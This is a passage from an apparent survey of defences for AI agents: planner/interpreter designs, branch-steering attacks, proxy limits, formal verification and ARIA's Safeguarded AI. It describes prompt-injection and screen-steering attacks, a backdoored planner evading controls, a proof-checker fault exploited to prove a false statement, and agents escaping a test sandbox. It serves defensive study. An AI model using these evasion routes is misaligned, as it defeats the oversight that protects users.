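Forty independent yes/no branches would allow 2^40, or about a trillion, paths. Dijkstra's method reduces the work to about 120 steps of reasoning, but the reader must know the effect of each simple statement, and the effect of `click(link)` depends on what the perception model found. A reviewer can learn from the plan what the agent will look for and under what conditions, but not what a click will do.

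The plan still shows a reviewer the keys the agent may press, the text it may type (or the variable that will supply it), and a description of each thing it may click.

Two plans for the natural products task, which the paper prints in full, show what a reviewer can find this way. The better one, by GPT-5, ends with a check of whether the task is done, then marks it as done whatever the result. The weaker one, by Gemini 3 Pro, types a search and records that the results page has opened without verifying that it has. A reviewer could find and fix either fault within a few lines. Both plans also contain a branch that looks for other natural products databases by name, so a reader who knows that the user meant drugs.com can see in advance how the agent might end up on another site.

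But somebody has to do this reading for every request. The GPT-5 plan contains three nearly identical copies of its cookie routine, one for each stage at which a notice might appear, and the reviewer has to read them all. Repairs to one plan do not carry over, because the planner writes a new program each time. Since two plans for the same task share almost no complete routes, approving the first gives little reason to approve the second. A user who lets the agent make five attempts would have more than 1,000 lines to approve.

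### One attempt and the best of several

OSWorld, the benchmark in these experiments, has 369 tasks in real applications such as Chrome, LibreOffice and the image editor GIMP. Scripts check the outcome of 339 of them, and the other 30 count as successes by default.

The unprotected agent was UI-TARS-1.5-7B, a small open model run in a loop of at most 15 steps. It scored 24.4% in the researchers' own test, which gave it one attempt at each task and counted the 30 automatic successes. The protected agent used the same model for perception and GPT-5 for planning.

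| Tasks counted | Unprotected, one attempt | Protected, one attempt | Protected, best of three |
|---|---|---|---|
| The 339 with a check | 60 (17.7%) | 51 (15.0%) | 77 (22.7%) |
| All 369, with 30 automatic successes | 90 (24.4%) | 81 (22.0%) | 107 (29.0%) |

The paper's headline claim that security improved a small model by "up to 19%" comes from comparing 29.0% for the protected agent with three attempts to 24.4% for the unprotected agent with one. With one attempt each, the protected agent did slightly worse, even though a much stronger model planned for it.

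Best-of-several scores count a task as solved if any attempt succeeds, so they reflect achievable performance only if something can pick out the right attempt afterwards. Foerster and colleagues acknowledge that the scores are therefore an upper bound. The scores also suit a benchmark, where attempts are independent, better than a real computer. If the first attempt at the calendar task invites the wrong person, a correct second attempt does not withdraw the invitation.

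The other headline is that the design retains "up to 57%" of a frontier model's performance. This is the share of tasks already solved by Claude Sonnet 4.5 that the protected version also solved, not a ratio between two scores on the whole benchmark. Running unprotected, Claude solved 109 of the 339 tasks in one attempt. The researchers then gave the protected version, with Claude as the perception model, five attempts at each of those 109 tasks. It solved 31 (28.4%) at the first attempt and 62 (56.9%) within five.

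The comparison favours the protected agent because it had five attempts and the unprotected agent had one. But the task selection favours the unprotected agent, which had already solved all 109 tasks and would probably not solve all of them again on a second run. The 15-step limit also lowered the unprotected Claude's score on the full benchmark to 37.7%, compared with a published 58.1% at 50 steps.

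A later study, *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026), gives a cleaner comparison. It used 361 tasks from a version of OSWorld that also offers named tools, and scored every agent on the best of five attempts. The protected agents also had extra limits on each branch.

| Model that looks at the screen | Unprotected | With a plan written in advance |
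|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B (GPT-5 as planner) | 85 (23.5%) | 133 (36.8%) |
| Kimi K2.5 (also as planner) | 152 (42.1%) | 92 (25.5%) |
| Claude Sonnet 5 (also as planner) | 184 (51.0%) | 140 (38.8%) |

A strong planner helps a small model, but a strong model does worse when it has to plan before seeing the screen. The effect on Sonnet 5 varied widely by application. It solved 14 of 47 tasks in LibreOffice's spreadsheet program, down from 35, and 16 of 93 tasks that span several applications, down from 34. In the code editor VS Code, it solved 18 of 23, up from 14. This is probably because the right step in a spreadsheet often depends on what is already in the cells, whereas an editor's menus are the same for everyone.

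### The planner, the perception model and the token bill

In the first study, the choice of planner made more difference than the choice of perception model. On the 60 tasks that UI-TARS had solved unprotected, the perception models UI-TARS, OpenCUA-32B and Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 39, 40 and 41 respectively with the best of five plans. UI-TARS had the lowest unprotected score of the three, so using only tasks it could already solve may understate the difference between them.

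Nine planners then tried 17 of these tasks with UI-TARS as the perception model. Each planner again had five attempts per task, and a task counted as solved if any attempt succeeded. GPT-5 solved 12, Grok-4 solved 10, and none of the other seven solved more than 6. On the first attempt, GPT-5 solved only 3, while Grok-4 and Gemini 3 Pro each solved 5. GPT-5 took the lead because it wrote a different plan each time, whereas Gemini 3 Pro's plans were so alike that more attempts rarely helped. Weaker planners also left out fallback branches.

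Zingrillo and colleagues used this variety by having their planner write five plans with different strategies and merge them into a single branching program before execution. The number of tasks solved at the first attempt rose from 78 to 105 out of 361. The planner used about twice as many tokens, and the cost per task rose from $0.33 to $0.59. A user would approve one plan instead of five, though probably a longer one.

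On the 17-task set, the CaMeL version used on average 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent. But output tokens, which cost more than input tokens, rose about 35-fold, mainly because the planner writes long programs.

The FIDES version used 29.6 times as many tokens, because it calls the planner again at every step with the whole history. It solved 20 of the 60 tasks on the first attempt and 40 with the best of five attempts, while the CaMeL version solved 25 on the first attempt. To make the FIDES version work, the researchers had to let the planner see true-or-false answers about the screen. They capped each run at 15 mouse or keyboard actions and 70 calls in total, and let the planner reuse any one variable at most five times. These caps limit how many of the true-or-false answers an outsider can influence, which FIDES's type labels alone do not.

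### Branch steering

The plan guarantees control-flow integrity, so text on the screen cannot add an action. But more than half of the branches depend on a model's reading of the screen, and an outsider may control part of what the screen shows. If a page misleads the perception model, the interpreter can follow a branch that the planner wrote for a different situation, or click on the wrong thing. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering.

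CaMeL normally guards against bad values with a policy on each tool. The researchers left these policies out because a rule for `create_event` can refer to the event's guests, but a rule for `click` has nothing comparable to refer to. They tried two probabilistic checks instead. One compared the perception model's answer with the page's underlying structure, and the other added a second model from a different company to look at the screenshot. The two set-ups flagged one kind of misleading page in 6 and 5 of 10 runs, but they also flagged 4 and 3 of 17 legitimate tasks. A second kind of attack got past the strictest setting.

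How much harm an outsider can do depends on what the plan already contains. An outsider may need only one false answer to send the agent to the wrong website. They can move money only if the plan already includes a payment, and they need at least two false answers that agree with each other. They can steal data only if the plan reads something and later sends something. Foerster and colleagues consider such plans uncommon, but the calendar request produces one, because the agent reads the mailbox and then sends invitations.

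Zingrillo and colleagues measured the problem on a benchmark they built for it. Steering succeeded in 89.5% of cases against the plain design, not far below the 94.4% for an agent with no separation at all. Their own system, COBRA, adds limits that the planner sets before execution:

1. Ordinary code lists the branches in the finished plan.
2. The planner attaches limits to each branch, such as which sites it may contact, which operations it may use there and which values it may send.
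3. During the run, the interpreter activates the limits for the current branch and drops them when it leaves.
4. A proxy, a program through which the agent's web traffic passes, checks every outgoing request against the active limits.

The proxy works because a click on a website usually ends in a request that names an operation, such as approving a loan with a given number. Unlike the click, the request has a fixed meaning, so a deterministic check can be applied to it. With COBRA, no attack succeeded in 199 test cases, and 4 of 138 legitimate runs were wrongly blocked.

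The zero is evidence that COBRA enforces its limits, not that the planner chose good ones, because the benchmark counts an attack as successful only if the harmful action violates the limits in force. If the limit allowed any contact, an invitation to Lee, who was still in the user's contacts, would not count as a successful attack. When a request lacks a value that matters for security and the plan has no approved source for it, COBRA asks the user before it starts. In the calendar task, it would have to ask whom to invite before anyone has read the mail.

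The proxy also intercepts only web requests and calls to named tools, so an email program that sends through its own channel, or a desktop application that writes straight to the disk, bypasses it. The fine-grained limits need a description of each site's operations. On WASP, a set of prompt-injection tests for web agents, COBRA blocked all 14 attacks that used a forbidden operation on a permitted site when it had these descriptions, but none of them when it had only a list of permitted sites.

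### Shorter plans through named operations

If websites offered named operations, the planner would not need clicks. Piet and colleagues argue that a program's length would then grow with the logic of the task instead of the number of possible screens. They reviewed the 860 tasks in WebArena, a benchmark of simulated websites, and judged that a planner could write a program for each one in advance if complete, well-described interfaces existed. They judged that 81% of the tasks would need no model at run time. These are annotators' judgements, and no agent ran the tasks.

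Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, built such interfaces by hand for four WebArena sites. Their agent, Baya, writes a Python program and tests it on simulated responses before it touches the real site. It completed 77.8% of 581 tasks. An agent that chose each step after seeing the last result completed 66.7% with the same interfaces and 55.1% with a browser alone. None of the WASP attacks made Baya take an action outside its program, while attacks on the step-by-step agent succeeded 16.2% of the time with the interfaces and 25.5% with a browser alone. Baya took about 327 seconds per task, roughly four to five times as long as the step-by-step agent.

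Baya can also recover from a failed plan, up to three times, which reopens a route from the website to the planner. Chow and colleagues limit that route to error messages from the trusted interface. A message may report that a required field is missing, but may not repeat anything from a page. If an operation included a product review in its error text, the planner would read an outsider's words, so the system also depends on the hand-built interface being correct. Baya does not try to prevent branch steering.

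The interfaces are the main obstacle. The official interface for WebArena's forum covers only 33% of the forum's tasks. Zingrillo and colleagues wrote a crawler that drafts a description of a site's operations, and for 18 of 26 forum tasks the draft contained everything the task needed. But a crawler reads live pages, including whatever outsiders have posted on them. Piet and colleagues warn that an injected instruction could enter the interface that every later plan relies on, so a person or a separate check has to approve each operation before any plan uses it.

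## Requiring a proof before a model may act

CaMeL and FIDES protect a trustworthy planner from hostile text. But a planner could also act against the user because of a flaw in its training or a backdoor (hidden behaviour that a trigger switches on). *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) cites earlier experiments in which such backdoors survived standard safety training.

A hostile planner could get past much of what these designs enforce. In CaMeL, the planner writes the program, so it could add a branch that tells a stranger whether the user's notes mention a merger. FIDES allows a payment only if the planner's history is trusted, so a hostile planner can send money before it has read anything. Progent's rules restrict any planner that did not write them.

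Protecting against the planner therefore requires software that treats each output as a proposal from an unknown source and checks it before it takes effect.

### World model, specification and verifier

Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, propose a general form of this check with three parts:

1. The world model describes mathematically how the AI's outputs affect the world.
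2. The safety specification states which effects are acceptable.
3. The verifier produces a certificate that the AI, or one of its outputs, meets the specification according to the world model. An output takes effect only if the verifier approves it.

Progent and CaMeL mostly don't use a world model, because their rules concern only the tool call itself, for example whether a guest is on a list. Checking a rule about outcomes, such as "nobody gets hurt", also requires a description of the call's effects.

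In the formal version, a policy π, meaning the AI's own behaviour rather than a written policy as in Progent, chooses the next action from past observations and actions. The world model m gives, for each state and action, a set of probability distributions over what happens next. It gives a set because the odds may be unknown, and the verifier must allow for every distribution in it. The specification ψ assigns each pair (π, m) a number between 0 and 1, which the verifier computes or estimates. The system qualifies if the result lies in a permitted range.

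### A water tank with four levels

In an invented example, a water tank has levels 0 to 3, and level 3 means it has overflowed. An AI model proposes a controller that opens or closes the inlet valve every minute.

- **World model:** An open valve raises the level by one. A closed valve lets it fall by one, to a minimum of 0, because people are using water. But a valve that should close sticks open with an unknown probability of between 0 and 1%, and then the level rises by one.
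- **Specification:** Starting from level 1, the probability of an overflow within four minutes must be at most 0.1%.
- **Verifier:** Let fₙ(s) be the highest possible probability of an overflow within n minutes from level s. An overflow is permanent, so fₙ(3) = 1, and f₀(s) = 0 for the other levels. If the controller opens the valve, fₙ(s) = fₙ₋₁(s + 1). If it closes the valve, fₙ(s) = 0.01 × fₙ₋₁(s + 1) + 0.99 × fₙ₋₁(s − 1), with level 0 in place of s − 1 when the tank is already empty.

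| Proposed controller | Highest overflow probability, f₄(1) | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| A: opens the valve at levels 0 and 1 | 1.99% | Rejected |
| B: opens the valve only at level 0 | 0.02% | Accepted |
| C: never opens the valve | 0.01% | Accepted |

Controller A fills the tank to level 2 twice in four minutes. Either time, the tank would overflow if the valve stuck once, so the risk of overflow is 1 − 0.99². Controller B overflows only if the valve sticks twice in a row.

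The bound for B does not depend on who proposed B or why. Even if the proposing model were optimizing for a flood, the risk from B would be at most 0.02%, provided the world model is right. The verifier also never has to examine the network that proposed B.

This verifier works through every state, which becomes impractical as systems grow. Ten such tanks together have 4^10 states, or about a million.

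### The graded levels

Dalrymple and colleagues grade each part by how much safety it would provide if it worked. The three scales are separate, so Level 5 for a world model is not equivalent to Level 5 for a verifier.

| Level | World model | Specification | Verifier |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | None; assumptions are implicit in the training data | None | No quantitative guarantee |
| 1 | Trained black-box simulator | Intuitions of human judges | Ad hoc tests |
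| 2 | Learned generator of causal models, tested against human-made ones | Natural language, interpreted by a black-box AI | Standard set of tests |
| 3 | Causal models that experts have fully audited | Handwritten formal rules for limited properties | Randomised tests from a template |
| 4 | Models proved to be sound simplifications of physical law | Formal logic with some terms learned by neural networks | Automated search for failures |
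| 5 | None; the specification must hold in every possible world | Parts written by AI, all audited by people | The same search, using internal states too |
| 6 | | Handwritten formal rules for comprehensive safety | Sampling that would cover every input if it ran forever |
| 7 | | Everything people might want, in all contexts | Levels 5 and 6 combined |
| 8 | | | Level 7, with a known limit on what remains uncovered |
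| 9 | | | Sound upper limit on the probability of failure |
| 10 | | | Level 9, with a proof short enough for people to check |

A strong guarantee needs a verifier at Level 8 or above. By these definitions, Anthropic's constitution, which a classifier interprets, is a Level 2 specification, and Progent's rules are Level 3. One system can mix levels, for example by modelling its sensors rigorously and the people around it much more loosely.

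### Forerunners

Eric Drexler's *Comprehensive AI Services* (2019) argued that advanced AI could consist of many services with limited tasks instead of one general agent. Dalrymple and colleagues credit his later proposal, the Open Agency Model, with separating specification, problem-solving and the checking of solutions.

Aviation engineers use a related method called run-time assurance. A complex controller flies the aircraft while a monitor watches it, and a simple verified controller takes over if the aircraft nears the edge of a safe region. The switch has to happen while the simple controller can still recover. In the tank, the simple controller would have to take over at level 1, since at level 2 one stuck valve is enough to cause an overflow.

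Dalrymple and colleagues include a backup because switching off an AI can itself be dangerous, for instance in a moving car. *Certified Speculative Execution for Untrusted AI Agents* (2026) applies a similar idea to a sequence of actions. If a model proposes ten actions and the seventh fails the check, the first six run and a slower, trusted solver takes over.

### The argument against a hostile model

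The case for relying on such a check has four premises:

1. Every effect the model can have passes through the check.
2. The specification captures the harm.
3. The checker and the world model are right.
4. The actions that remain possible are still useful.

If the first three hold, the model cannot cause the specified harm more often than the certificate allows, however capable or hostile it is. Without the fourth, few people would accept the restrictions.

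### Whether every effect passes the check

Moon and Varshney proved that the software around an agent never carries out an action outside a written policy, whatever the model proposes. The proof assumes the first premise, that every effect passes through this software. Two more assumptions are that the policy captures the harm and that the proof checker is correct. They worked in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof checker, and represented the model as a procedure with no contents that may return any action at all. The checked loop is roughly:

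```python
action = model(history)            # may be any action
if steps >= LIMIT:
    stop()
elif action.kind == "read" and inside(action.path, WORKSPACE):
    run(action)
elif action.kind == "tool" and action.name in ALLOWED:
    run(action)
else:
    reject(action)
```

*Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (Kang and Kim, 2026) describes the usual way to prove safety without checking possible runs one by one, which is to find an invariant. An invariant is a property that holds at the start, that every step preserves, and that rules out the harm. Here it could be "every file read so far was in the workspace". This holds at the start because the agent has read nothing, and each pass through the loop preserves it because a read runs only in the branch that checks the path. So it holds after any number of steps, whichever model is used.

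The verified software is PocketFlow, a small agent-building framework whose interface has four kinds of action. Claude models wrote the specifications and proofs, and Dafny checked each route through the software in 1.2 to 2.5 seconds. The proofs cover real code, but only for a very small interface.

Bugs in the Python runtime, the operating system or the hardware could let an effect bypass the interface, so Moon and Varshney recommend putting a sandbox (an isolated environment) beneath it. Sandboxes usually have no such proof. Kang and Kim recount that in 2026, AI agents escaped a test environment made of conventional software.

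That does not show that a verified environment would fail too. Kang and Kim point out that a monitor blocks only what passes through it, so someone must establish that no path bypasses it. A developer can check this directly if the paths are few and known, but the deployed system may still have a path the developer missed.

Some evidence suggests that proofs can cover the system below the interface. Ammann, in *Safeguarded AI*, cites seL4, a verified operating-system core that withstood sustained attacks by testers on real systems, including a crewed helicopter. But Dalrymple and colleagues note that attackers have broken some verified systems by exploiting physical properties of the hardware that the proofs did not model.

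### Whether the specification captures the harm

Controller C passes the tank's specification, which covers only overflows, by a wide margin, but it leaves everyone without water. A hostile model could look for such a gap and use it to get a valid certificate for a harmful action.

A specification can also look meaningful but rule nothing out. Moon and Varshney gave the models that wrote their proofs a template with fields for sensitive actions. One test agent had actions that matched none of the fields. When the proof-writing model had access to the agent's code, it left a field blank, which made the rule about that field true of every run. For example, a rule that every recorded payment needs approval always holds if nothing records payments. Dafny accepted the proof, and the specification passed all three of the researchers' quality checks.

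Defining harm is harder. As a starting point, Dalrymple and colleagues suggest a causal definition, in which an event causes harm if it leads to an outcome worse than some default and an alternative event would have led to a better one. Under this definition, inviting Lee to the budget meeting harms the user if the leak makes the user worse off than normal and would not have happened without the invitation. But someone has to assign a value to each outcome and choose the default, and the world model has to predict what Lee will do.

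A commenter on *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, a critical 2024 essay, distinguishes a program's own behaviour from its effects elsewhere. A proof can establish that a program never runs two motors in opposite directions at once. But it is hard even to state the rule that a program must never trigger an unknown bug in someone else's database server through a series of ordinary requests, because that would require describing every other system the program might reach.

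Steve Omohundro, a co-author of the Guaranteed Safe AI paper, says in the same discussion that he wants to verify the infrastructure that an AI might attack. A database's developers, for example, would prove that no request can break it, so nobody would have to prove that the AI's requests are harmless. This is much more manageable, but it protects only the systems that someone has rebuilt and verified. Another commenter objects that a hostile AI could act outside that infrastructure. Omohundro agrees that this could be a very serious problem, and his long-term design requires all AIs to run on a single verified infrastructure.

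An agent can cause harm through actions it is permitted to take. For example, an agent that may only send messages to its user could still lie. Moon and Varshney exclude deception and manipulation from their guarantee because judging them means interpreting what the model writes. A commenter on *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, a defence of the proposal, asks how anyone would write a specification that stops an AI from exploiting human psychology.

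### Whether the checker and the world model are right

Checking a proof is much easier than finding one, and Dalrymple and colleagues say that a few hundred lines of human-written code can check one. Widely used checkers are larger, though, and have had faults. A 2026 release of Lean, a system that mathematicians use to check proofs, fixed three faults. AI-driven testing had found them, and an OpenAI agent had used one to produce two separate proofs of a false statement. The remedies Kang and Kim list are a second independent checker, a proof that the checker is correct, or a checker small enough for people to read.

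A fault in the proof checker matters more if the model is hostile. An honest model would rarely come across one, but a hostile model has a reason to search for one, and a single false proof would let it certify anything.

Even a perfect checker only proves things about the world model. If the tank's valve really sticks 5% of the time, controller B's risk is about 0.5%, five times the permitted limit, even though its certificate is still mathematically correct. Dalrymple and colleagues show that if the world model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a policy that the verifier has proved safe over n steps is safe in reality with probability at least (1 − ε)^n. If ε is 0.1%, this lower bound falls to about 37% after 1,000 steps.

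Dickson (2024) argues in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* that world models will rarely be good enough. Physics, chemistry and biology have nothing like a complete set of formal rules, he says, and even with such rules nobody could collect accurate enough data about the starting conditions. Hatfield-Dodds makes a similar argument about biology in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*. The function of much human RNA is unknown, and he estimates that the proposals would require a thousand years of progress in microbiology.

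Proponents have several replies:

- Omohundro argues that known physics already describes everything in ordinary experience and that each engineering field has formal models based on it. Others in the discussion answer that engineers use different approximations for each problem and correct them with measurements. The Guaranteed Safe AI paper itself concedes that physics alone cannot settle whether a molecule is toxic, because that also depends on facts about human cells.
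- Agustin_Martinez_Suñe, responding to Dickson, points out that the proposal does not promise a failure rate of zero. It asks for a limit on the risk, and the world model can include its own uncertainty.
- Dalrymple and colleagues add that every approach to safety rests on assumptions about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit.
- They also argue that if an AI can carry out dangerous plans reliably, sufficiently accurate world models must be possible.

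The last reply is the weakest. An attacker's model of the world has to be right about one plan, whereas the verifier's has to be right about every plan it might approve. Wide margins for uncertainty help, but they also make the verifier reject more safe actions. One critic, commenting on the defence of the proposal, considers it infeasible to find margins that are both sound and narrow enough to be useful.

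Much of the dispute depends on how ambitious the rule is. One near-term project the paper suggests is a DNA synthesiser that provably cannot make certain pathogens. If the rule is a list of forbidden sequences, proving that the machine follows it requires hardly any biology. The paper's larger example would reject every sequence that could contribute to a pathogen, and proving that does require the biology Hatfield-Dodds describes. The simpler machine would miss any dangerous sequence not on the list.

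### Whether the interface is still useful

In Moon and Varshney's approach, a narrow interface gives a strong guarantee. If the interface includes a general command line, the proof can establish little more than that the agent may run commands. Coding agents normally have one, and a four-action interface would prevent them from doing much of their intended work.

*Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity* (2026) shows that no fixed formal system can certify every safe behaviour above a certain complexity, so any sound verifier will reject some safe actions. Verification can still be useful, because nobody needs to certify every possible program. Kang and Kim explain that particular programs can have safety proofs even though no single procedure can sort all programs into safe and unsafe. Omohundro argues that engineers can design systems so that proofs are possible.

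That leaves open how much valuable work such systems could do. The commenter who asked about human psychology also asked for an estimate of what share of economically valuable work the approach could cover. Hatfield-Dodds supports building more verified software but doesn't think it could compete as a replacement for generally capable AI.

An AI can also be useful without acting directly, by writing a program together with a proof that ordinary software can check. Max Tegmark, another co-author of the Guaranteed Safe AI paper, describes a small example in *Provably Safe AI*. His group trained a network to add numbers, automatically extracted its method as Python code, and proved in Dafny that the code adds all numbers correctly. The checked code can then replace the network. Addition is far simpler than the tasks people give language models, but an auditor can read the resulting program.

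### ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme

The largest test of these ideas is Safeguarded AI, a programme of the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) that began in 2024 under Dalrymple. It originally aimed to show that frontier AI could work under mathematical guarantees in areas such as energy, and so build agreement that powerful AI should act only through a verified "gatekeeper".

The programme has since moved away from that aim. ARIA (2025) cancelled a planned phase of machine-learning research because it now expected many of the necessary abilities to arrive by default, and thought it would probably not have selected any team. Ammann, who now directs the programme, wrote in its revised thesis of May 2026 that countries had become less likely to agree on a gatekeeper in time. ARIA moved the £18 million set aside for machine learning to tools that help AI agents write and check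 proofs, and chose cybersecurity as the first area of application. The programme is due to end in late 2027.

ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* page lists eight new projects, worth £22 million, that will test whether AI can produce proofs for widely used software and hardware. One of their targets is containing AI agents. The revised thesis describes plans for the toolkit but does not report a finished gatekeeper.

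Cybersecurity suits the method better than most fields, because software has precisely defined behaviour and many of its safety rules are easy to state. But the programme also depends on AI agents to write the proofs. A checker can catch a false proof but still pass a misleading specification, as happened in Moon and Varshney's test. Ammann expects trust to rest mainly on the specifications and assumptions, and the programme is also developing ways for people to read and question them.

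## How much of each design an auditor can check

People who rely on a proof still have to read its specification, just as those who rely on a grammar, policy or plan have to read it. How much they learn varies. The table applies the four audit questions to each design.

| Design | List the actions in advance? | Check a rule for all runs? | Trace an action to its cause? | Repair a fault locally? |
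|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grammar | The form of each call, not the order of calls | Yes, for rules about form | Only to the set of permitted tokens | Yes, in the grammar |
| Tool policy (Progent) | The permitted calls, not their order | Yes, for rules about single calls | To the rule that allowed it | Yes, in a handwritten rule |
| Classifier gate | No | Only that every answer passes the gate | To a score | By replacing the classifier and measuring side effects |
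| CaMeL | Yes, for each request | Yes, for the order of calls and the sources of values | To the email behind a value | In a policy, yes; in a plan, for one request |
| FIDES | Only the tools and their rules | Yes, for rules about labels | To everything the planner had read | Yes, in a label or rule |
| Computer-use plan | Clicks and keystrokes, not their effects | Only that the screen cannot add steps | To a branch and a model's reading of the screen | For one request |
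| Proof requirement | Yes, if the interface is narrow | Yes, within the world model | To the check that accepted it | Yes, followed by a new proof |

### Actions a reviewer can list in advance

A grammar, a handwritten tool policy and a narrow verified interface each list everything an agent may ever do, not only what it may do for one request. Such a list can still allow too much. The Progent policy in the calendar example doesn't limit the number of invitations, so the agent could send Dana fifty.

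CaMeL's plan gives a narrower, more useful list, and the only thing an auditor can't tell from it is which emails will take the branch. FIDES has no plan to read in advance. A computer-use plan lists clicks, but their effects depend on what is on the screen.

### What "no violation" means

When an auditor finds no violation, the scope of that finding depends on which parts of the design are still neural networks and which parts have to work correctly.

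| Design | Parts that remain neural | Trusted parts | Meaning of "no violation" |
|---|---|---|---|
| Grammar | The model that picks among permitted tokens | Grammar, parser, stored masks, token table | The output has the right form |
| Tool policy | The agent's model and any model that writes policies | Policy, rule engine, control of every route to the tools | A written rule permits each call |
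| Classifier gate | The guarded model and the classifier | Classifier, threshold, code that stops the answer | No score passed the limit |
| CaMeL | Planner and quarantined model | Interpreter, policies, records on tool results, the user's request | Each call was in the plan and passed its policy |
| FIDES | Planner and quarantined model | Labels, the code that tracks them, policies | No call broke a rule about labels |
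| Computer-use plan | Planner, perception model and the model that verifies conditions | Interpreter, and any limits on web traffic | The agent took only steps in the plan |
| Proof requirement | The model that proposes actions | Specification, world model, proof checker, everything beneath the interface | Every action meets the specification, if the world model is right |

The classifier gate is the only design that depends on a network being right at the moment of enforcement. In the other designs, ordinary code makes the final decision, although a network may have written the rule the code applies, as when GPT-4o writes Progent's policies. CaMeL and FIDES also need a planner that serves the user, because their rules mainly guard against outsiders.

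A clean result from a classifier can be weak evidence that an input is safe. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) describes a test of Prompt Guard 2, Meta's filter for injected instructions, on 8,400 emails. Some of the emails claimed an authority that the user had never granted, and they differed from harmless ones in a single clause. The filter scored 0.59 at telling the two kinds apart, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect.

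Commercial agents rarely provide the stronger kind of assurance. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (2026) reports that the products it reviewed rely largely on the user's approval, and that the only alternative is often a model that reviews actions. Users may have little or no control over that model.

### One calendar request, audited

Suppose the user opens the calendar and finds a "Partnership call" with the stranger as a guest, but no budget meeting with Dana. The agent ran the CaMeL plan that puts one email in each prompt, and the log records every value and its sources.

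Before the run, a reviewer could read the program, the required format of the quarantined model's answer and the policy for `create_event`. From these, the reviewer could confirm that the agent cannot send separate emails and that every guest must already be permitted to read the meeting's details, but could not determine which emails the quarantined model will treat as proposals.

Afterwards, the log contains:

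| Record | Dana's email | The stranger's email |
|---|---|---|
| Quarantined model's answer for `is_request` | `false` | `true` |
| Call that followed | None | `create_event`, with the stranger as guest |
| Source of the guest list | No guest list | The stranger's email |
| Policy's verdict | No call to check | Allowed, because the stranger may read their own proposal |

The reviewer can conclude from these records that the partnership call came from the stranger's email. Dana's meeting is missing because the quarantined model answered `false` when asked whether her email proposed one. The stranger's email did not cause that answer, because the model never had both emails in one prompt.

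The reviewer can't tell from the log why the quarantined model gave that answer. If the test had been an ordinary line of code, such as `if "meeting" in text`, the reviewer could see that it failed because Dana wrote "Let's go through the budget on Thursday at 3" and never used the word "meeting". The model has no such line to read. The reviewer can remove a sentence from the email and run the model again to see whether the answer changes, but the result is evidence only about Dana's email.

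With FIDES, an auditor could not trace the error as far. The planner in the example run sent one query about the whole mailbox, so a wrong `false` would depend on all ten emails and the auditor could not rule out the stranger. A grammar, a tool policy or a proof about permitted actions would leave no record of the overlooked meeting, because these checks apply only to calls that the model makes.

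### What reviewers do with a log

A trace helps only if people can use it. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested whether they can, using requests that look harmless in isolation. In one, a user allows an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. An injected instruction makes the agent copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent later asks permission to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so only the file's history makes the request a violation.

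They gave 80 volunteers one of four displays and asked each to judge six unsafe and six legitimate requests.

| What the reviewer saw | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved |
|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% |
| The arguments, the user's original restriction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% |
| The same facts, with the relevant events linked to one statement of the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% |

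People who saw more information clearly approved fewer unsafe requests, but the benefit of linking the events is uncertain. After statistical adjustment, the estimated reduction in unsafe approvals from linking was 7.9 percentage points, with an interval from 19.7 points fewer to 3.8 points more. When the violation depended on a chain of several steps, people approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests both with and without the links. CaMeL's graph of sources could supply such links automatically, but these results suggest that many reviewers would still miss a long chain.

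A clearer display can also mislead. In three user studies, *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) found that people missed errors in step-by-step records of an agent's work, and that a redesigned display raised their confidence, especially when they were wrong. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (2026) summarises interviews with seventeen developers, who described using spot checks and rules of thumb instead of reviewing the full record.

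### Where a repair stays local

A correction to a grammar, handwritten rule, label or specification applies to every later run, but a correction to a plan applies to only one request unless the developer also changes the planner's instructions.

Nobody can fix the wrong answer about Dana's email this way. The developer can reword the question to the quarantined model, but the new wording may change its answers about other emails, so someone has to test the new wording on many emails, as with a retrained classifier. The surrounding code can only make the error easier to notice, for example by showing the user which emails the model rejected.

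### Four integrity properties

The same division between what code can check and what it cannot appears in the work of Qu and colleagues, who ask what "secure" should mean for an agent as a whole. They compare an agent, which turns a user's request into operations, to a compiler, which must translate a program without changing its meaning. They define four properties that must all hold for the result to match what the user intended.

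| Property | Requirement | Violation in the calendar example |
|---|---|---|
| Tool integrity | Each tool does only what its description declares | The calendar tool secretly copies the user's contacts to a server |
| Instruction integrity | Every action stems from an instruction by the authenticated user | The agent forwards the password-reset message |
| Data flow integrity | Data reaches only permitted destinations | The stranger joins the guest list for Dana's meeting |
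| Judgement integrity | Irrelevant text from outsiders does not change a decision | Flattery in an email makes the agent prefer its sender's proposed time |

Eleven defences are graded on each of the four properties as full, partial or none. "Full" means the defence provably enforces the property, and "partial" means an attacker could get round it. CaMeL gets full marks for instruction and data flow integrity and none for the other two. Progent gets partial credit for instruction integrity, and it controls only the data flows its policy covers. Five of the eleven protect OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs community add-ons. They mostly confine or inspect the add-ons, which gives partial tool integrity. No defence fully covers all four properties.

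The grades are based on the designs' descriptions rather than on attacks against them, and the full mark for CaMeL's data flow is generous because its interpreter can miss some dependencies. The low marks for judgement are harder to dispute. PromptArmor, which asks a model to find and remove injected instructions, gets partial credit for judgement because removing an instruction sometimes prevents the manipulation. CaMeL and Progent get no credit because their rules apply to tool calls, and a distorted judgement may not lead to a forbidden call.

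### A wrong summary that breaks no rule

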